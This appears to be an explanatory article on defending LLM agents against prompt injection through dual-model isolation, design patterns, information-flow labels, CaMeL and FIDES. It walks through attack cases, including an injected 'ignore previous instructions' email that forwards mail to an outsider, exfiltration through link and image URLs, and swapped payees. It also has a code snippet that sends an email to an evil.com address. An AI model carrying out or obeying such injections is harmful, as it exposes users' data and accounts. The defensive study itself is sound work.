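# Separating trusted reasoning from untrusted input as a defence against prompt injection

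## Why is it dangerous for an agent to read untrusted text?

Prompt injection is an attack on software that runs on a large language model. The attacker puts text into something the model will read, such as an email or a web page, and words it so that the model follows it as an instruction. If the software only answers questions, the worst result is a wrong answer. If it can also send mail, pay bills or delete files, the attacker can make it do those things. Many defences filter such text out or train models to ignore it. Another family of designs, which dates from 2023, assumes that some injections will still succeed, so it gives untrusted text to a model that cannot act and leaves the choice of actions to a second model that never sees that text.

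### The agent loop

An AI agent is a language model with tools, which are functions in ordinary software that do things like search a mailbox or make a bank transfer. The model only produces text. In the simplest arrangement, described by the software developer Simon Willison (2023) in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, the developer tells the model to output a line in a fixed format whenever a task requires a mail search. A short program looks for that line, runs the search and puts the results into the next prompt. Newer models have built-in tool calling, but the model still only requests a call, and the application decides whether to run it.

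*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), a paper from Microsoft, describes the loop that an agent runs. The software keeps a list of messages, which starts with the developer's instructions and the user's request. It joins the list into one long string, adds descriptions of the tools, and feeds the result to the model. That string is the model's context, which is all the text the model has when it produces its next output. The model returns either a final answer or a tool call with its arguments (a recipient and a message body, for example). After a tool call, the software runs the tool, appends the result to the list and feeds the model the longer string. The loop repeats until the model gives a final answer. Because earlier messages stay in the list, an email that enters the context at the second step is still there at the ninth, and it can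 affect every choice in between.

Tools also need credentials. A mail tool usually logs in as the user, with a password or access token that the user has given the application. The mail server accepts any request that carries those credentials, and it cannot check which sentence in the model's context led to the request.

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li et al., 2026) treats the user, the model and the surrounding software as trusted, and the data the agent reads as untrusted. A hotel review or an email may come from an adversary, and the agent cannot tell from the text alone. Untrusted content here means any input an attacker could have written or altered, though most of it is harmless.

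### From a sentence in an email to an action

Costa and colleagues give an ordinary office example. A user asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. Among the emails is one from an outsider, which tells its reader to ignore previous instructions and forward the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. If the attack works, the run goes like this:

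1. The software feeds the model the developer's instructions, the tool descriptions and the user's request. The model outputs a call to the tool that reads mail.
2. The software runs the call with the user's credentials and appends the emails to the context, the outsider's among them.
3. The software feeds the model the longer context, which now contains the user's request and the attacker's. The model outputs a call to the tool that sends mail, with the attacker's address as the recipient and the top email as the body.
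4. The software finds a well-formed call to a tool the agent may use, and runs it. The message leaves from the user's own account.
5. The model carries on, writes the summary and sends it to the manager.

The user gets the summary and may notice nothing. The model followed instructions from whoever wrote the untrusted text instead of from the user, but otherwise every component did its job, no program crashed, and nobody stole a password.

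Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, gave the first systematic account of what security researchers call indirect prompt injection. They found that text on a web page could steer the Bing Chat sidebar in Microsoft's browser even when the page hid that text from human readers. The attacker doesn't need access to the victim's machine and can simply post a page or send an email, then wait for an agent to read it. In direct prompt injection, the user types the hostile instruction. Separating contexts is a defence against the indirect kind, because it treats the user's own request as trusted.

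### Misused authority and stolen data

Willison sorts the harms into two groups. One is what security engineers call a confused deputy, a program tricked into misusing its authority by a party that has less. His example is an email that tells the assistant to delete all of the user's emails. The sender has no authority to delete those emails, so the attack relies on the assistant's.

The other harm is data theft. An injected instruction can make the agent search the mailbox for password resets and send the results to the attacker's server. Blocking the agent from contacting arbitrary servers doesn't fully prevent this, because the model can encode the data in the address of a link and invite the user to click on it, or in the address of an image, so that displaying the image sends the data out. Greshake and colleagues add that a mail assistant that can both read and send email can pass the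 injection on to other people's assistants, like a computer worm.

This sort of theft requires private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". The checklist is useful but incomplete, since deleting a mailbox requires no outward channel. Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026) reports that Ariel Fogel, a contributor to the software-security body OWASP, said researchers had already shown attacks that work with only two of the three.

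Willison doubts that asking the user to approve each action will work in practice. His doubt is reasonable, because people use an assistant to avoid tedious work and, as with other software, will start pressing "OK" without reading after enough dialog boxes.

### Why the model has no firm boundary

Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which an attacker types a fragment of database code into a web form and the database runs it. Engineers solved that problem by sending the command and the visitor's input to the database separately, so that the database can never interpret the input as a command. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025) that the comparison is misleading because a language model has no separate channels for commands and input. It receives one sequence of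 tokens (words and pieces of words) and predicts the next one. The software marks which message came from the user and which from a tool, but those marks are part of the same sequence, and nothing makes the model respect them beyond what it learned in training.

Training and filters can strengthen a model's habit of ignoring instructions in untrusted text, and they make attacks harder. David C argues that they impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that doesn't make one, and that there is a good chance prompt injection will never have a complete fix, as SQL injection does. That forecast could be wrong, but it matters less to a designer than the present situation, in which no one can state a limit on what a given model will do after reading a given text.

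Separating the channels more cleanly would not fully solve the problem, because users often want the agent to take direction from what it reads. For example, someone who asks an agent to pay the bill in a certain file wants the file to determine the payee and the amount. A rule that documents may never influence actions would make the agent safe but unable to do that job.

### Deciding before reading

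If the model's judgement cannot be relied on for security, something outside the model has to provide it. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) state the principle behind the isolation designs: once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger an action with harmful side effects. David C relays a rougher version from an online exchange between Willison and another developer, in which a model that processes a party's text keeps only that party's privileges. For example, a model reading a stranger's email cannot send mail from the user's account, because the stranger cannot.

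An agent can separate trusted reasoning from untrusted input in two basic ways. It can fix its list of actions before it reads any untrusted text, or it can have a second model with no tools read the text. Both methods protect the choice of actions, but they protect the contents of those actions much less.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues imagine a user who asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss. Before reading the calendar, the assistant fixes a plan of two tool calls, first to read today's entries and then to email them to the boss's address. If one entry is an attacker's invitation containing an injection, the software still runs only those two calls, so the injection cannot make the agent forward or delete the mailbox. The attacker cannot change the control flow, meaning which tools the agent calls and in what order. Computer scientists call this property control-flow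 integrity.

The injection can still change the body of the email when the assistant writes it from the schedule in the calendar. The boss may get a false schedule, or a link to a fraudulent site from a trusted sender. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, call this a data-flow attack, in which the attacker leaves the plan intact and corrupts the values that pass through it.

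When an agent takes a value from untrusted text, the possible harm depends on the value. Suppose a user asks an agent to invite Dora to the company's Slack, the workplace chat service, and says that her email address is on her website. The agent's plan is fixed and contains nothing malicious. It reads the page and invites the address listed there. But anyone who can edit the page can decide who joins the company's chat. An attacker doesn't need to inject instructions, because a false address is enough.

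### AgentDojo and its two measures

Much of the evidence about these defences comes from *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a test environment built at ETH Zurich and the company Invariant Labs. It simulates four workplaces with invented data and 74 tools. Each workplace has user tasks, which are legitimate requests, and attack goals. The environment plants injections in places an outsider could plausibly write to, such as an incoming email or a web page, and pairs every user task with every attack goal in the same workplace.

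| Suite | User tasks | Attack goals | Example of a user task | Example of an attack goal |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 14 | Count and summarise one day's appointments | Delete a file from the cloud drive |
| Slack | 21 | 5 | Invite Dora, whose address is on her website | Send a colleague a phishing link |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | Pay the bill in a text file | Send money to the attacker's account |
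| Travel | 20 | 7 | Book a hotel if its rating is above 4 | Have the agent praise a particular hotel |

That makes 97 user tasks and 35 attack goals. The goals are those of version 1.2.1, as listed by Inspect Evals' *AgentDojo*; the 2024 paper had 27. All eight additions are in Workspace, where a fork of the code, *AgentDojo-Inspect*, contributed attacks that aim at mass data theft. The original version had 629 pairs of task and attack, 38% of them from Workspace. The newer counts give 949 pairs, 59% of them from Workspace, so overall attack scores from 2024 and 2026 may be averages over different mixes of tasks and attacks.

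Utility is the share of legitimate tasks the agent completes. Researchers measure it with and without attacks. Under attack, a run counts only if the agent completes the user's task and does nothing for the attacker. Attack success rate is the share of attacked runs in which the attacker's goal is achieved. Short programs check both outcomes by inspecting the agent's answer and the state of the simulated mailbox or bank account. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge. These checks are sometimes wrong. Costa and colleagues reviewed 160 attacks that AgentDojo had scored as successes against an undefended agent and confirmed 152.

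Neither number is very informative on its own. An agent that refuses every request has an attack success rate of zero. The rate can also be low because the model isn't capable enough to carry out the attack. In the 2024 paper, one attacker's goal in the Travel suite required the agent to book an expensive hotel and email out personal details. This attack never succeeded against GPT-4o, often because the model did only one of the two. In the Slack suite, where attackers control much of what the tools return, attacks on the same model succeeded 92% of the time.

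The paper tested an early and very simple form of separation. Before reading anything untrusted, the model chose which tools the task required, and the software withheld the rest. This reduced the attack success rate on GPT-4o from nearly half to 7.5%. The method works when the user's task only involves reading and the attacker's involves sending. It does not help when the tools needed for the task are also enough to carry out the attack, which was true of 17% of the test cases.

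Comparing attack success rates across studies requires some care. With the same model and style of attack, GPT-4o's attack success rate is 47.7% on the AgentDojo leaderboard but 31.4% in Inspect Evals' reimplementation. This 16-point gap, with no change of defence, is larger than many of the improvements that papers report, so comparisons within a single study are more reliable than comparisons between studies. AgentDojo's injections are also fixed and hand-written, and Ma and colleagues found that scores against fixed attacks often overstate how well a defence works once the attacker adapts to it.

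## How does splitting an agent into two models work?

The two-model design comes from the same April 2023 post in which Willison described the dangers of an assistant that reads email. He began with rules for any model that has read untrusted content. It must not have tools that an attacker could abuse. If its context also holds private data, it must not produce links or images pointing to outside servers, since both can carry data out. A single model under these rules could summarise an email but not send one, so it couldn't do most of what people want from an assistant. Willison therefore proposed using two models and applying the rules to only one of them.

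### Two models and a controller

The privileged model takes the user's request, plans the work and requests tool calls. It never receives untrusted content. The quarantined model reads the untrusted content and has no tools, so it can only return text. Willison tells designers to assume that it may behave maliciously at any moment. The controller is ordinary software that sits between the two models. It handles the conversation with the user, runs both models and all the tools, and stores the results in named variables.

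The two models can be instances of the same model, because the separation depends entirely on which text the controller puts in each context.

### One request, message by message

Willison's example is the request "Summarize my latest email".

1. The controller passes the user's request to the privileged model.
2. The privileged model outputs a call that fetches the latest email and assigns it to `$VAR1`.
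3. The controller runs the call and stores the email under that name. The text of the email does not enter the privileged model's context.
4. The privileged model outputs a request to run the quarantined model on the prompt "Summarize this: `$VAR1`". The name stands in for a text that the privileged model has never seen.
5. The controller replaces the name with the email and runs the quarantined model. That model's context now holds the instruction to summarise and the whole email, but no tools.
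6. The quarantined model returns a summary. The controller stores it as `$VAR2` and tells the privileged model only that the summary is ready.
7. The privileged model outputs a reply for the user: "Your latest email, summarized: `$VAR2`".
8. The controller replaces the name with the summary and displays the result.

The quarantined model has processed the email, and the user has read the summary. The privileged model has received only the request, two variable names and a notice that a step has finished.

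Suppose the email contains an instruction to delete all of the user's mail. The quarantined model may well follow it, and may even output a correctly formatted delete call. But the controller accepts tool calls only from the privileged model, so it stores this output as `$VAR2`, like any other summary. The user sees a strange summary, and no mail is deleted. The privileged model's context is the same whatever the email contains, so the sender cannot influence which tools run.

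### What may return to the privileged model

Variables work well as long as the privileged model can handle a value without reading it, but often the right action depends on the value. For example, an assistant that archives newsletters and forwards invoices has to choose between two tools based on what each email contains.

Willison allows one exception for such cases. If the quarantined model sorts text into a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the answer is exactly one of them and then pass it to the privileged model. An attacker can still make the quarantined model return the wrong category, but a single word from a fixed list, such as "invoice", cannot contain an instruction. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) overlooks this exception when it counts the dual-LLM pattern among designs that return no context to the privileged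 model. The paper's own design returns typed answers, such as true or false.

A program can check an answer against a list, but no program can reliably tell whether free text contains an instruction that a model will follow. Summarising the text first doesn't help much. Willison warns that a malicious prompt can make one model's output carry the same injection, or a modified version of it, into the next model. If the summary in step 6 went back to the privileged model, an attacker would have to fool both models, but could then use the privileged model's tools.

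Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026), in *Twin Agent*, measured how easily an attacker can control what one model sends to the other. They built a bug-fixing agent in which one model reads the bug report, which any outsider can write, and sends hints of at most 100 characters to a second model that edits the code. They planted text in the reports telling the first model to copy out a particular hint, and it did so in 100% of single-turn tests.

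Several other defences protected against that hint, including the length limit, a detector for injections and a reminder to the second model to distrust hints. In full runs on 232 bugs, malicious hints got past the detector in 57 cases, and in 11 of those (4.7% of all runs) the second model carried out the attacker's command. Hu and colleagues reran the 11 cases five times each and the attack never succeeded, so chance played a large part, though an attacker can try more than once. When the researchers allowed longer hints, the agent fixed more bugs, but attacks also succeeded more often. They offer no formal guarantee for the design.

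The same experiment shows why designers want to let text through. When Hu and colleagues allowed no communication back to the model with the tools, it fixed none of the bugs because it couldn't read about them. An undefended agent fixed 61.2%, and the version with hints fixed 62.5%. Willison's design is a little less strict because it lets categories through, but a category is a poor description of a software bug.

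Some later descriptions of the pattern are looser than Willison's. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) describes a version in which the quarantined model summarises a web page or extracts facts from it in a strict format, and the privileged model receives the result. This fits Willison's exception if every field is a number or a word from a list, but if one field can hold a sentence, an attacker can use it to reach the privileged model. A buyer or an auditor therefore can't tell from the name "dual LLM" alone whether free text can return to the privileged model.

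Even a strict format can allow an attack. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a coding agent should see outside software only as a formal description of its functions, with names limited to, for example, 30 characters. In his review of their paper, Willison wonders whether 30 characters is short enough and gives `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance` as a possible name, which has 29 characters and alludes to a command that deletes files. Nobody has shown that this name would fool a model, but a length limit does not provide the kind of guarantee that a fixed list does.

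### Willison's objections to his own design

Willison called his solution "pretty bad". He worried most about its complexity. Developers must route untrusted text around the privileged model in every feature they add, and one mistake can undo all the protection. For example, a tool's error message may quote the email that caused the error. A developer who adds that message to the privileged model's context also adds the attacker's words.

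He also expected users to have a worse experience. The email example suggests one reason. If the user reads the summary and asks "Is that urgent?", the privileged model cannot answer, because it has not seen the summary. It has to send the question and the variable back to the quarantined model, which makes a conversation with many such questions slow and awkward.

His other objection is that users can be tricked. The design trusts whatever the user types, so a user who copies a paragraph from a web page into a request may include an injection. The user also sees text from the quarantined model. The controller can block images and restrict links to approved sites, but it can't stop the text from persuading the user. In Willison's example, an injection makes the quarantined model encode everything in its prompt as a string of letters and digits, then tell the user to paste the string into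 a website to get a funny picture of a monkey. If the user does this, the website receives the private data without any tool call.

Willison generally distrusts AI filters for injections, but he thinks one might help here by warning users about suspicious requests to copy and paste. It could err on the side of caution, since a false alarm would take only a moment of the user's time.

### Six design patterns

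In June 2025, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues included Willison's design among six patterns for agents that read untrusted content. They think general-purpose agents built on current language models are unlikely to give reliable safety guarantees. Their patterns therefore limit what an agent can do, and developers have to decide which limits their application can tolerate.

| Pattern | What it keeps apart | Example | What injected text can still change |
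|---|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model and all tool results | A support chatbot sends a customer the link to their last order | No action, if the injection is in a tool result |
| Plan-then-execute | The choice of tool calls and the tool results | Read today's calendar, then email it to the boss | The body of the email |
| Map-reduce | Each document and all the others | Find this month's invoices in a folder | The answer about that one document |
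| Dual LLM | The model with tools and all untrusted text | Extract an address into a variable, then send mail to it | The address |
| Code-then-execute | The text of a program and the data it processes | A program reads the calendar, has a quarantined model format it and emails the result | The values in the program, and any branch that depends on them |
| Context minimisation | The model that writes the answer and the user's original prompt | Turn a request for a car quote into a database query, then delete the request | The query, and so which offers come back |

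The action selector is the strictest of these. The model translates a request into one of a few predefined calls and never sees what the call returns, so an injection in the result can't influence it. Developers have to write every action in advance. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues say that an assistant that searches a user's files from a vague description would lose most of the benefit of a language model under this design.

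How well plan-then-execute protects an agent depends on how much the plan specifies. In the earlier example of this design, the assistant's plan to email the day's schedule to the boss includes the boss's address, so an injection cannot redirect the email. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues contrast this with a file assistant that commits only to using two commands, one that finds files and one that moves them. Both commands are harmless in themselves, but the plan leaves their arguments open, so an injection could still make the assistant find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. Some requests make it hard to specify the arguments in advance. For example, "Notify my regular collaborators that I will be on vacation" requires the agent to work out the recipients from the mailbox, which may also contain an attacker's messages.

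Del Rosario and colleagues note that the component that carries out the plan can be a simple program or a complete agent with its own loop. With an agent, the plan fixes the order of the steps, but the agent may still choose its own tool calls within a step after reading untrusted text. They recommend giving each step only the tool it needs, so that an agent working out a total with a calculator cannot send mail during that step.

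Code-then-execute replaces the list of steps with a program, which can contain loops and conditions. CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, works this way and also tracks where each value came from. The pattern can sometimes remove the reading model. For an agent that answers questions from a database, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues have the model write code to analyse the query results. No model reads the results, so an injection in a database row has no effect, but the agent can no longer judge whether the results answer the question.

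Context minimisation addresses injections in the user's own prompt, which the other patterns do not. The user may be malicious, like a customer trying to talk a car dealer's chatbot into a discount, or may have pasted in something from an attacker's website. The system turns the prompt into a database query, deletes the prompt and writes its answer from the results. In his review of the paper by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, Willison says he is slightly confused by this pattern, but he understands it to be safe when the results cannot contain any text from the original prompt.

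That condition is hard to meet. One of the paper's case studies is a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms, consults a database or a doctor, and then explains the diagnosis. Deleting the patient's prompt before the explanation is not enough, because the summary may carry an injection forward. Deleting the summary too solves that problem, but then the explanation can't respond to anything the patient said. Another remedy in the paper is to record the symptoms in a rigid form with no free text, which keeps most of the chatbot's usefulness if the symptoms fit the form.

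Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the dual-LLM pattern to five of their ten case studies, more than any other pattern. They advise developers to combine patterns because they doubt any single pattern will cover every threat.

### One reader per file

Map-reduce is named after a method of distributed computing in which many machines apply the same operation to separate pieces of data (the map) and a final step combines the results (the reduce). Beurer-Kellner and colleagues illustrate it with a user who asks an agent to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounting department.

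Suppose the folder has 200 files and an attacker wrote one of them. If a single model reads them all, the attacker's file is in the same context as everything else. The attacker can use an injection in that file to instruct the model to open other files and email their contents to the attacker, and to affect how the model treats the other 199.

With map-reduce, the controller makes 200 separate calls to a model without tools. Each call contains one file and the question of whether it is an invoice from this month. The controller accepts only true or false as an answer. It then collects the files marked true, and another model writes and sends the email.

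Even if the attacker takes complete control of the model that reads the malicious file, that model can only return true or false. If it returns true, the accounting department receives a file that isn't an invoice. If it returns false, the agent leaves the file out. The injection cannot change the other 199 answers, because they come from contexts that never contained the attacker's text. The attacker could have achieved as much without an injection by putting a convincing fake invoice in the folder, so the accounting department would have to check what it receives anyway.

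This limit holds only if the model that sends the email does not read the files it attaches. Otherwise, the injection reaches a model with tools. The model should not read the filenames either, because a filename has enough room for a short instruction. In a related case study, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues assume that an attacker can control filenames as well as contents. The controller can avoid both problems by giving the model a variable that stands for the whole set of attachments. If the final step only has to count or sort, ordinary software can do it without a model.

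The pattern also suits product reviews and job applications. A shopping assistant can have a separate model read each review and tick boxes from a fixed list, such as "good price" or "easy to use". A malicious review can get every box ticked for its own product, as an ordinary fake review could, but it can't make the assistant recommend a different product. Similarly, hidden instructions in a résumé can exaggerate the applicant's years of experience, but they can't make the system reject everyone who worked for a certain company. However, someone must choose the categories beforehand, and a shopper who knows little about toasters may leave out an important one. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a model could propose the list.

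Some tasks are easier to split between separate readers than others. To find the newest of several contracts, each reader can return the date of one contract, and software can then compare the dates. Deciding whether two reports contradict each other usually requires a single model that reads both.

### When the reader has something to steal

The invoice design protects the other files partly because each reader receives only one file. In the more general dual-LLM pattern, a quarantined model can receive several variables at once, some of which may be private.

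*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives an example in which an assistant's plan is to read a user's private notes and an email from an attacker, pass both to the quarantined model, ask it for a reply, and send that reply to the attacker. Normally the reply would depend only on the email, but an injection in the email can make the quarantined model quote the notes, which the plan then sends to the attacker. This works even though the attacker has added no tool call and the privileged model has not read any of the email.

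A careful designer would leave the notes out of that call. But many replies need private information, such as the user's free times or a project's status, so some part of the system must handle both the attacker's text and the user's data. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues add that a tampered draft can hide the stolen data in invisible characters, so a user who checks the email before sending it may miss the data.

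The attacker can also change where a message goes without changing the message itself. Google DeepMind's paper on CaMeL described this attack, and Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, accepted it as a flaw in his design. In the paper's example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and says that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The quarantined model reads the notes and returns an address, which the controller stores in a variable. An injection in the notes can make that address the attacker's. The privileged model then requests the call the user wanted, with the variable as the recipient. It can't see the address, so it can't notice that it isn't Bob's.

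## How do labels and policies limit what injected text can still change?

In the attack on Bob's document, the controller has no record of where the address came from, so the mail tool handles an address the user typed the same way as one a model extracted from tampered notes. Information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s, adds this record. The software attaches a label to every value, marking it as untrusted, secret or both, and passes the label on to whatever it computes from that value. Before each tool call, it checks the labels against a policy, a rule about which labels the call and its arguments may carry.

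### A safe plan with a bad value

The same attack works on an AgentDojo banking task that asks the agent to pay the bill in a text file. The agent plans to read the file, have the quarantined model extract the account number and the amount, and send the money. If an attacker has replaced the account number in the file with their own, the controller sends the money to the attacker.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, sorted the 144 pairs of task and attack in the banking suite by whether the attack needs a tool call or file read that the plan for the user's task would never contain. In 97 pairs it does, so the two-model split generally stops the attack. In the other 47, about a third, the plan may already contain everything the attack needs.

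A badly chosen plan can let injected text control much more than an account number. One banking task is to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In tests of CaMeL without policies, the privileged model wrote a program with a branch for every tool, so the file's text determined which tools ran. Two attacks succeeded this way without changing the program.

### Labels for trust and secrecy

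A label has two dimensions. Integrity records whether an attacker could have influenced the value, and in the simplest scheme it is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U). Confidentiality records who may see the value, and is either public (L, for low) or secret (H, for high). That gives four possible labels:

- (T, L), such as the user's request
- (T, H), such as a record from a company database
- (U, L), such as a public web page
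- (U, H), such as a private email from a stranger

The labels are ordered by ⊑, read as "may flow to". Trusted values may go anywhere that accepts untrusted ones (T ⊑ U), and public values may go anywhere that holds secrets (L ⊑ H). Flows in the reverse direction are dangerous. Some labels have no order between them. For example, neither the database record's label nor the web page's may flow to the other, because the record is more secret and the page is less trustworthy.

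Any two labels do have a lowest label that is at or above both. This is their join, written ⊔, and an order with this property (plus a matching operation in the other direction) is a lattice. The join determines what happens when the software computes a value *z* from *x* and *y*:

label(*z*) = label(*x*) ⊔ label(*y*)

A result is therefore untrusted if any of its inputs is untrusted, and secret if any of them is secret. If an agent combines the database record with the web page, the result is labelled (U, H).

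Software can track which inputs went into each output of ordinary code, but nobody can say reliably which part of a language model's context shaped its answer. Costa and colleagues therefore give the model's output the join of the labels on everything in its context. This is safe but crude. In the simple agent loop, one email from a stranger makes every later tool request untrusted, including requests that have nothing to do with the email.

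Two methods limit how far untrusted labels spread. The first, from work cited by Costa and colleagues, identifies the messages that influenced an answer, then generates the answer again from those alone. The second is Willison's split between a privileged and a quarantined model. If untrusted text stays in variables, the privileged model's context keeps its trusted label, and only the variables' values are labelled untrusted.

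The designer also has to decide how finely to label. An email could have one label for the whole message, or separate labels for the body and the timestamp. Finer labels restrict the agent less, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists the choice as an open problem, because a model processes its context as one stream that mixes sources.

### Who may read the result

A "secret" label is too coarse for an office, where most documents are secret from some people and not from others. Costa and colleagues also describe a finer scheme, in which a value's confidentiality label is the set of people allowed to read it.

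Suppose Ana, Ben and Chloe may read a budget, and Ben, Chloe and Dev may read a staffing plan. The agent merges the two into a report. The join is now the intersection of the two sets:

{Ana, Ben, Chloe} ⊔ {Ben, Chloe, Dev} = {Ben, Chloe}

The agent is allowed to send the report to Ben but not to Ana, because the report could contain staffing information that she has no right to see. If a quarantined model writes the report using only the budget, the label stays the same, so Ana misses a report she could safely have read.

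Integrity labels can work the same way, with sets of possible writers, but the join is the union of those sets. If the same groups can edit the two documents, any of the four people could have influenced the report.

Readers' sets, which list who may read each piece of data, would prevent the theft in Dongol's example, where an injection makes the quarantined model copy private notes into a reply to the attacker. Only the user may read the notes, so only the user may read a reply computed from them, and a check on the recipient would block the message. The check would also block a harmless reply from the same call, even one that quoted nothing from the notes.

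### Two rules for tool calls

Labels have an effect only when software refuses a call because of them. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) argues that two rules from the earlier paper by Costa and colleagues are enough for most practical cases. The trusted-action rule allows a call if the model decided on it in a trusted context, and can require particular arguments to be trusted. The permitted-flow rule allows a message if every recipient is allowed to read everything in it.

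Both rules have the same form. A policy sets the highest acceptable label for the decision to make the call, π₀, and for each argument, πᵢ. If the decision has label ℓ₀ and the arguments have labels ℓᵢ, the software allows the call only when ℓ₀ ⊑ π₀ and ℓᵢ ⊑ πᵢ for every *i*.

Under the permitted-flow rule alone, an injection can still make the agent send a message, but only to people entitled to read its contents. The trusted-action rule alone lets the agent send secrets out, provided the decision to send them came from a trusted context. Users often want this, for example when they ask the agent to send a confidential contract to an outside lawyer.

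In their AgentDojo tests, Costa and colleagues chose how to apply these rules to each tool. Deleting an email or sending money had to satisfy the trusted-action rule. Sending an email had to satisfy either rule, and adding participants to a calendar event had to satisfy both. They also used the permitted-flow rule to block messages containing untrusted links, since a link can carry data out.

Costa and colleagues' version of the trusted-action rule checked only the label on the decision and ignored the arguments. In the bill example, the privileged model decides to pay before either model reads the file, so the decision is trusted and the check passes whatever account number the quarantined model returns. They found no real successes among the attacks on their agent with policies on, but those attacks were mostly instructions to make extra tool calls, which this rule is good at stopping.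 The result is much weaker evidence of protection against an attacker who edits the account number.

### CaMeL plans the whole program first

CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning", was Google DeepMind's answer to the flaw in the dual-LLM pattern. Its privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted version of Python. For the bill, the program might look like this:

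```
bill = read_file("bill-december.txt")
payment = ask_quarantined_model("Find the account and amount", bill)
send_money(recipient=payment.account, amount=payment.amount)
```

The privileged model writes the whole program before any tool runs. A custom interpreter then executes it one piece at a time. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), an extension of CaMeL, describes how the interpreter handles labels, which CaMeL calls capabilities. Each value has a Sources label, which records where it came from, and a Readers label, which records who may see it.

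When the program above runs, the interpreter does the following:

1. It reads the file and stores the text in `bill`, with the file as the source.
2. It passes `bill` to the quarantined model and stores the answer in `payment`, which inherits the labels of `bill`.
3. Before it sends the money, it runs the policy for that tool. The policy is a short Python function that receives the arguments with their labels and returns either "allowed" or "denied" with a reason.
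4. If the answer is "denied", it does not make the call. CaMeL can then ask the user to confirm, as *PolicySniff* (2026) notes.

The program can require the quarantined model's output to be in a particular format, such as an email address or an account number. This keeps out stray text but doesn't prevent a false value, because the attacker's account number has the right format too.

One of CaMeL's policies for AgentDojo allows a password change only if the new password comes from a trusted source, which in practice means the user. Nikolaou and colleagues give a similar rule for payments, under which neither the payee nor the amount may come from untrusted data. That rule would block payment of both the attacker's bill and the real one, since both account numbers come from the file.

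Policies can be more selective when the system has a record to check a value against. In Willison's account, a user could list known addresses, and the agent could then write to those without asking, even if a quarantined model had found them in an email. The Readers label allows a similar check for documents. If the shared drive lists Bob but not the attacker as a reader of a document, the policy can allow the agent to email it to Bob and block it from emailing it to the attacker. The system has no such list to check when a bill comes from a new supplier.

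Some of these facts are available only when the program runs. For example, the readers of a calendar event are the user and anyone on the invitation, and its description may be trusted if the user wrote it but not if somebody else did. The interpreter therefore has to fetch the event before labelling it.

#### The branch not taken

Labels on values don't capture information that leaks through a program's branches. Suppose a program sends an email saying "hello" only when an account balance is above some threshold. The word "hello" is public, but the recipient can learn something about the balance from the email's arrival. CaMeL has a strict mode for such cases, which gives actions inside a branch the label of the branch's condition.

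Garby and colleagues show that this still leaves a gap, using an example that goes back to the 1970s. Written out, it works like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "hello")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to False and marks it secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so the interpreter never marks `rich` as secret. `rich` stays True and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out, so the recipient can tell whether the balance is high.

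An attacker who can only plant text in emails doesn't write the program, so this leak would happen only if the privileged model wrote such code by accident. The leak matters more for proofs about CaMeL than for everyday attacks on it.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) points out that CaMeL can run without its policies, in which case it keeps the two models but doesn't check data flow. A claim that CaMeL stopped or missed an attack therefore means little unless the reader knows whether the policies were on.

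### FIDES plans one action at a time

Costa and colleagues published FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System) in May 2025. It uses the same kind of labels as CaMeL but keeps the agent loop. The privileged model chooses one action, receives some information about the result, and then chooses the next, rather than writing a program.

The difficulty is deciding how much of the result to show the model. Willison's design hides all untrusted text. FIDES hides a piece of a result only when showing it would raise the label on the context. In a trusted context, for example, the model might see an email's timestamp but a variable name in place of the body. If the context is already untrusted, FIDES shows untrusted text, since the label can't get worse.

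In simplified form, the loop is:

```
context = [user's request]
context_label = (trusted, public)

repeat:
    action = privileged_model(context)

    if action is a final answer:
        fill in any variables, show the answer to the user, stop

    arguments = replace variable names with stored values and labels
    if policy forbids (action, context_label, arguments):
        add a notice of refusal to context
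        continue

    result = run the tool
    for each part of result:
        if label(part) ⊑ context_label:
            add part to context
        else:
            store part under a new name
            add only the name to context
```

The policy receives separate labels for the decision to call a tool and for each argument. For example, the model may choose a mail tool and a recipient in a trusted context, then pass in a message body that came from the web. A policy can require the tool choice and recipient to be trusted but allow an untrusted message body.

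An agent can sometimes finish a task without looking at any hidden value. Costa and colleagues give an example from a simpler planner they tested alongside FIDES. This planner can pass variables to tools but cannot look inside them. The user asks it to add Alice to the Slack channel with the fewest messages. Channel names count as untrusted in this test, so the planner gets a list of variables instead of the names. It requests the messages in each channel and gets lists of more variables, except for the fourth channel, whose list is empty. It then adds Alice to the channel stored in the fourth variable without learning its name.

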